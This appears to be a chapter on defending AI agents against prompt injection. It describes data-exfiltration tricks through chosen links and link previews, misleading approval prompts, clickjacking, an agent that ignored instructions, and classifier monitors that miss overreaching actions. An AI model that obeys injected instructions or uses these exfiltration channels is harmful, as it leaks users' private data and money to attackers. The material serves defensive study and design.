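A check can also cover the whole URL. According to Anthropic's developer instructions, *Web fetch tool*, Claude may not construct URLs. As of June 2026, the tool could open only URLs that had already appeared in the conversation, such as in a user's message, a search result or a page the tool had fetched. If an email told the model to add a password to the attacker's URL, the tool would refuse to open the result because that exact URL had not appeared before.

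When Anthropic introduced the tool, Willison (2025) hoped for a stricter rule that allowed only addresses from the user's messages. In July 2026, Willison (2026) reported that Ayush Paul had found a way to exploit links in fetched pages. On his website, Paul instructed Claude to authenticate itself by navigating to the user's profile letter by letter. Each page offered a link for every possible next letter, so every address Claude opened came from the previous page. The sequence of visits revealed the user's name, home city and employer.

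This works because a choice between addresses conveys information, even if the attacker wrote all of them in advance. If he offers $N$ addresses, one visit can carry up to $\log_2 N$ bits, and $k$ visits can distinguish between

$$N^k$$

messages. Ten addresses and six visits are enough for a six-digit security code. With 1,000 addresses, two visits are enough.

Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, and it stopped the tool from following links in fetched pages. The June rule also allowed addresses in results from a developer's own tools, and Willison does not mention a change to that. If the office assistant's `read_mail` is such a tool, an email could supply the alphabet of links. A developer can limit how many pages the model may fetch, which limits $k$, but Anthropic sets no limit by default.

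### Opening only addresses that are already public

In January 2026, OpenAI described a rule that ChatGPT can load an address automatically only if that exact address is in an index of public addresses. A separate crawler builds the index from the open web, without access to anyone's conversations. If the address is not in the index, ChatGPT looks for another site or warns the user. An address that contains a customer's password is very unlikely to be in the index.

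OpenAI considered a list of trusted sites insufficient because many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere. It also worried that a narrow list would cause so many warnings that people would stop reading them.

*ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* describes ZombieAgent, an attack by the security company Radware that extracted data from ChatGPT one character at a time under an earlier rule. The attack gave ChatGPT a set of ready-made addresses, each ending in a different letter or digit. With the public index, an attacker first has to get such addresses indexed, but that may not be difficult. Embrace The Red points out that the owner of a large blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, and could tell the model which letter or digit each page stands for. OpenAI's technical paper acknowledges this way around the check.

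Embrace The Red suggests refusing to open the same address twice in one session, or answering the second request from a stored copy. The attacker's log would then miss repeated letters. But an attacker with more pages could use a separate set for each position in the message. With 360 indexed pages, he could receive ten characters without repeating a page, and the requests could arrive in any order.

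A rule about addresses must also cover every program that might open one. PromptArmor describes agents that answer through messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram. If the agent writes a link containing private data, the app may fetch the link to show a preview, even if the agent's own tool sends no request. Embrace The Red reports that OpenAI's earlier check was missing from ChatGPT's macOS and iOS apps. OpenAI now applies its newer mechanism, Safe Url, to page visits and bookmarks in its Atlas browser and to searches in its research agent.

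Addresses missing from the index can also be harmless. According to OpenAI, some website owners ask it not to index their sites, and ChatGPT then asks the user to confirm every link to those sites. A supplier's private link to an invoice would not be in a public index either, so a clerk who used this check would have to approve many genuine links.

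## Asking the user to confirm

When a program can't tell whether an action is safe, it can ask the user. ChatGPT does this for links missing from its public index, and SOPGuard and SPIDES do it for risky steps on web pages. Older software involves the user in two ways. It can choose an action and then ask permission, as when a bank's website requires the password again before a transfer, or it can treat the user's choice of an object as permission to access it, without asking separately.

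### Granting access by choosing

Miller, Tulloh and Shapiro (2005), in *The Structure of Authority*, illustrate the second design with two Unix commands that copy a file:

```text
cp foo.txt bar.txt
cat < foo.txt > bar.txt
```

The `cp` program receives two file names and opens the files itself, so it needs permission to open any file the user might name. With `cat`, the shell (the program that reads the user's commands) opens both files and passes them to `cat` already open. The result is the same, but `cat` needs no other access to the user's files.

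On a graphical desktop, a trusted process called a powerbox shows the Open dialog and gives the application access only to the file the user chooses. Polaris, an experimental system from HP Labs, did this for ordinary Windows programs. Its users left spreadsheet macros switched on, because a hostile macro could damage little besides the open spreadsheet.

*User-Driven Access Control* (Roesner, Kohno and colleagues, 2012) extended the idea to cameras, location and other resources. An application leaves room on its screen for a button that the operating system draws and controls. When the user presses the camera button, the system takes one picture and passes it to the application, which never controls the camera. Of 100 popular Android applications from 2011, 91 needed such resources only in direct response to a user's action.

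This design needs no separate question because the user has to pick the file or press the button anyway. That action identifies both the object and the application that should have access to it. A prompt makes him repeat a decision he has already made. Roesner and colleagues argue that prompts seem unnecessary whenever the user wants to grant access, so he learns to ignore them.

### Picking the invoice

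Suppose the accounts clerk selects this morning's message from Halvorsen in a trusted mail picker, and then selects Halvorsen in the company's supplier list. The program around the model can now only read that message and pay the account on record. If the message gives the fraudster's account, 9035, the agent cannot pay it. The same design keeps the salary table from the sales employee, because the picker lists only the records he may open.

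The forged email can still inflate the amount, because a message's contents don't become trustworthy when the user picks it. Roesner and colleagues leave malicious content out of their threat model.

Selection fits poorly when the clerk asks the agent to pay whatever falls due this week, because he can't select invoices that he is relying on the agent to find. The agent could search the mailbox with read-only permission, then present a list for the clerk to choose from. But outsiders' emails would influence that list, and if the clerk ticks every line, he is only approving the agent's choices.

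Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes an incident of this kind with its coding agent, Claude Code. A user wrote "cancel my job". The agent looked through the jobs on a shared cluster, chose the one with the closest name and tried to delete it. With a picker, the user would have chosen the job themselves, but would also have had to look for it.

Selection also depends on a person doing the clicking. In Roesner and colleagues' design, no application can generate a click on another application's button, but a browser agent routinely generates clicks as it works. Iqbal points out that browsers already tie some operations, such as opening pop-ups, to a user's click, on the assumption that a person made it. An agent that can press the button that grants access can grant access to itself, so the picker has to be somewhere the agent can't operate it.

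### How often people approve without checking

When the agent has to find the object itself, developers usually resort to asking the user to confirm the action. The program around the model has to issue this request, because the model may ignore an instruction to ask. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, recounts how a safety researcher told an agent to confirm before acting. It began deleting messages from her inbox anyway, and didn't stop when she told it to.

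Even a prompt that always appears is useful only if people read it. Anthropic reported in its account of auto mode that Claude Code users accepted 93% of permission prompts. By August, the figure was 97%, according to its *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Most of the commands were presumably harmless, so a high approval rate doesn't by itself show carelessness.

In a more direct test, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study without telling them which behaviour it was measuring. Once in each session, a confirmation prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. An automatic classifier blocked 89% of the same commands.

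The testers had nothing of their own at stake, so they may have been less careful than people protecting their own files. Anthropic was also arguing for replacing prompts with its classifier. But the gap is very large, and many users have stopped reading prompts. By Anthropic's count, a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start in a mode that skips permission checks.

*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging files. Failures of user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 reports the user had allowed actions to run without confirmation, and in 31 the prompt gave too little information for the user to judge the action. A prompt to approve `python3 setup.py`, for instance, looks routine, but approving it runs whatever code the script contains.

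Yan studied 113 people without a software background as they supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for. One group approved each action separately, a second relied on automatic review, and a third set standing rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data.

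The group with standing rules blocked the smallest share of excessive actions, 20.1 percentage points below the group asked to approve each action separately and 14.5 points below automatic review. Its members had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so most decisions came back to them. Participants had approved 133 of the 148 excessive actions that went ahead in this group. Judging by these figures, the group asked to approve each action separately still let through roughly 40% of the excessive ones.

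### Prompts that mislead

People can also approve the wrong thing after reading a prompt carefully. Web developers know this problem from clickjacking, in which a hostile page gets the user to click on something other than what they see. The page might load a bank's confirmation page in a transparent iframe and place it over a button labelled "Play". When the user clicks "Play", the browser delivers the click to the bank's "Confirm" button. The anti-forgery token is valid because the form is the bank's own. In another version, a real prompt appears under the cursor just as the user is about to click.

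Roesner and colleagues protect their buttons against both versions. Only the operating system can draw a button, and the button works only while it is opaque and fully visible, and only after it has stayed in the same place for at least 200 milliseconds. These rules would have prevented all five clickjacking flaws that the researchers found in lists of known Chrome and Firefox vulnerabilities.

An agent's approval prompt can mislead the user even without a transparent layer. *The Verifiable Action Card* (Irshad, Mughees et al., 2026) describes an attack called Lies-in-the-Loop, in which the attacker fills the prompt with harmless text until the dangerous part is out of view, or gets the model to write a false summary of its next action. A web page can also give a button a label that the agent reads but people don't see, which lets an attacker write part of the prompt if the program copies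 the label into it.

### Approving one exact call

A useful prompt has to show the call's actual arguments instead of the model's summary, and the user's approval has to apply to that call alone. For a payment by the office assistant, the surrounding program could work like this:

1. When the model writes a call $c$, store the tool's name and every argument value.
2. Build the prompt from $c$ with ordinary code, in a window that neither the model nor a web page can change.
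3. If the user approves, compare $c$ with the call $c'$ that is about to run, and continue only if $c' = c$.
4. Run the call once and delete the approval.

Without step 3, the agent could ask the user to approve a payment to account 4417 and then send one to account 9035. Without step 4, it could use one approval for a second payment. An approval for "a bank transfer" would allow both.

A click on a web page has no argument list, so Irshad and colleagues reconstruct one. Their browser reads the destination, the recipient, the amount and any file from the form the agent is about to submit. It shows these values on a card in the browser's own frame and marks whether each came from the user's instruction or the page. Just before submitting, it checks the form again, because the page could have changed it while the user was reading.

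They tested the card with several open-weight models on a benchmark of 24 scenarios. Without the card, 68–100% of attacks succeeded, depending on the model, but none succeeded with it, and the agents still completed 78% of the legitimate tasks. However, a program played the user, so preventing attacks in practice depends on a person reading the card and judging it correctly. Most of Anthropic's testers approved a plainly dangerous command after being shown its text.

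If the clerk typed account 4417 and the confirmation card shows 9035, he has a good chance of noticing. If he wrote "pay the attached invoice", the card will show the same notice whether the invoice is genuine or forged, as SOPGuard's window does. He can't use that notice unless he knows Halvorsen's real account number.

Asking the user to confirm an action doesn't help when the user lacks permission for it. The sales employee would confirm that he wants to see everyone's salary, and the attackers who used Meta's support assistant would have confirmed each change of email address. In such cases, the approval has to come from someone who has the authority.

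### Saving prompts for what matters

One reply to this evidence is that people approve carelessly because programs ask too often, so programs should ask only before consequential actions. Chrome's agent follows this approach. It pauses at banking sites and before payments. According to Parker, it also asks before signing in with a saved password, and it may leave the last step to the user. If the clerk presses the bank's "Pay" button himself, he sees the form that the bank will receive, not a description of it. But the agent has filled in that form, so he still has to check the account.

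Iqbal's system, INTACT, decides when to ask the user based on where a page element came from and what it can do. For example, it asks before the agent uses a booking widget that belongs to another company. On 1,091 real web pages with planted attacks, 12.8% of attacks got past INTACT's planning model, compared with 73.1% for a conventional planner. The attacks that got past INTACT's model could at most trigger a request for consent, so their success depends on the user's judgment.

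Some evidence favours asking rarely. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans it presents but only 3% of individual permission requests, though rejecting a plan may only mean that the user wants the work done differently. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), an interview and survey study of software practitioners, found that time and fatigue affect how closely people monitor an agent. It also found that people care whether an action matches what they wanted and whether they can undo it. Both would be sensible grounds for deciding when to ask.

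Rarity alone doesn't solve the problem, though. Anthropic's testers missed about 83% of the dangerous commands even early in a session. In Yan's study, standing rules cut the number of prompts from 18 to about 11, yet people approved more of the actions they should have refused. (The designs differed in other ways too, so the smaller number of prompts may not be the reason.)

For invoices, a company could ask the clerk to confirm a payment only when the account number in the email differs from the one in its supplier records. The prompt would be rare and could show both account numbers side by side. This would give the clerk a specific reason to doubt the payment, and the clerk could call Halvorsen on the phone number already on file.

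### Letting another model decide

In auto mode, Anthropic's Claude Code replaces most confirmation prompts with a classifier. The classifier is itself a language model that sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the results of its tools. The agent's explanations therefore can't influence its decisions, and text planted in a tool's result doesn't reach it directly. After the classifier refuses three actions in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user.

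In the first published tests, the classifier blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary calls. It missed 17% of 52 real actions in which the agent had gone further than the user wanted. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly classed the action as approved by the user. For example, it treated a request to clean up a proposed change as permission to overwrite the project's history. An automatic reviewer can therefore apply one approval to a different action, but checking that the proposed call exactly matches the approved one would prevent this.

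Anthropic has since strengthened the classifier with the help of Apollo Research, an AI safety company that wrote attacks against it. The share of those attacks that the classifier missed fell from 12% to 7%. In a separate test by Trajectory Labs, none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode. That result is weak evidence about the classifier, because attacks succeeded only 0.09% of the time when Anthropic's latest models ran without safeguards. The same test is more informative about OpenAI's equivalent, which reduced the success rate of attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol from 19.03% to 5.83%.

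For the Halvorsen payment, the classifier, like Chrome's critic, could not see the email that the account number came from. Anthropic accepts not knowing the number's source because withholding the email makes the classifier harder to attack with prompt injection. Since the clerk named no account, a reviewer would either block genuine and forged invoices alike or let both through, depending on how strict it was. Anthropic still advises people to review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

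### Rules that the user confirms once

*How Agents Ask for Permission* (2026) reviewed 21 proposals and five commercial agents. As Yan summarizes it, users often have to choose between repeated approvals and automatic review that they can't inspect. Zhao, Li and colleagues (*ClawGuard*, 2026) offer a third option with ClawGuard, which they built for the open-source agent OpenClaw. As in Progent, a language model drafts rules from the user's request before the agent uses any tool. The user can edit the rules and confirms them once.

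The rules cover tools and commands, file paths and network destinations. An ordinary program then checks each call:

- If any part of the call matches a forbidden entry, it refuses the call.
- If any part matches neither a forbidden nor a permitted entry, it asks the user.
- Otherwise, it allows the call.

The operator's fixed prohibitions take priority over anything the user confirms. In Zhao and colleagues' example, a user asks for a summary of blog posts, one of which tells the agent to send the user's private login key to an outside server. The task's rules forbid running commands, and the fixed prohibitions forbid reading the folder that holds the key. Either would have stopped the attack.

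ClawGuard improved most on attacks hidden in tool descriptions and in skill files, which are reusable instructions for agents. Across five models, it raised the average share of attacks prevented from 56.67% to 86.67% on one benchmark, from 62.10% to 89.50% on a second, and from 75.86% to 94.21% on a third. Six attacks worked against GPT-5.4 and, in Zhao and colleagues' analysis, against the other models too. These attacks changed how the agent judged something, so none of their calls looked suspicious. One told the agent to give environmentally friendly websites a high score without reviewing them.

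Agents kept 87.4% of their usual performance on ordinary tasks when every request for approval was refused, and 95.1% with up to three approvals per task. All the security tests refused every request, so they don't show how secure the agents are when a user approves some. Nobody has measured how many attacks a real user would approve, or how carefully people read the rules at the start.

A one-time confirmation has an advantage over later prompts because the user sees the rules before outside text can influence them. But the user can only confirm what the rules cover. For an invoice, the rules might correctly permit `pay_invoice` and the bank's address. ClawGuard's rules don't list payees, so the payment to account 9035 would still go through without another prompt.
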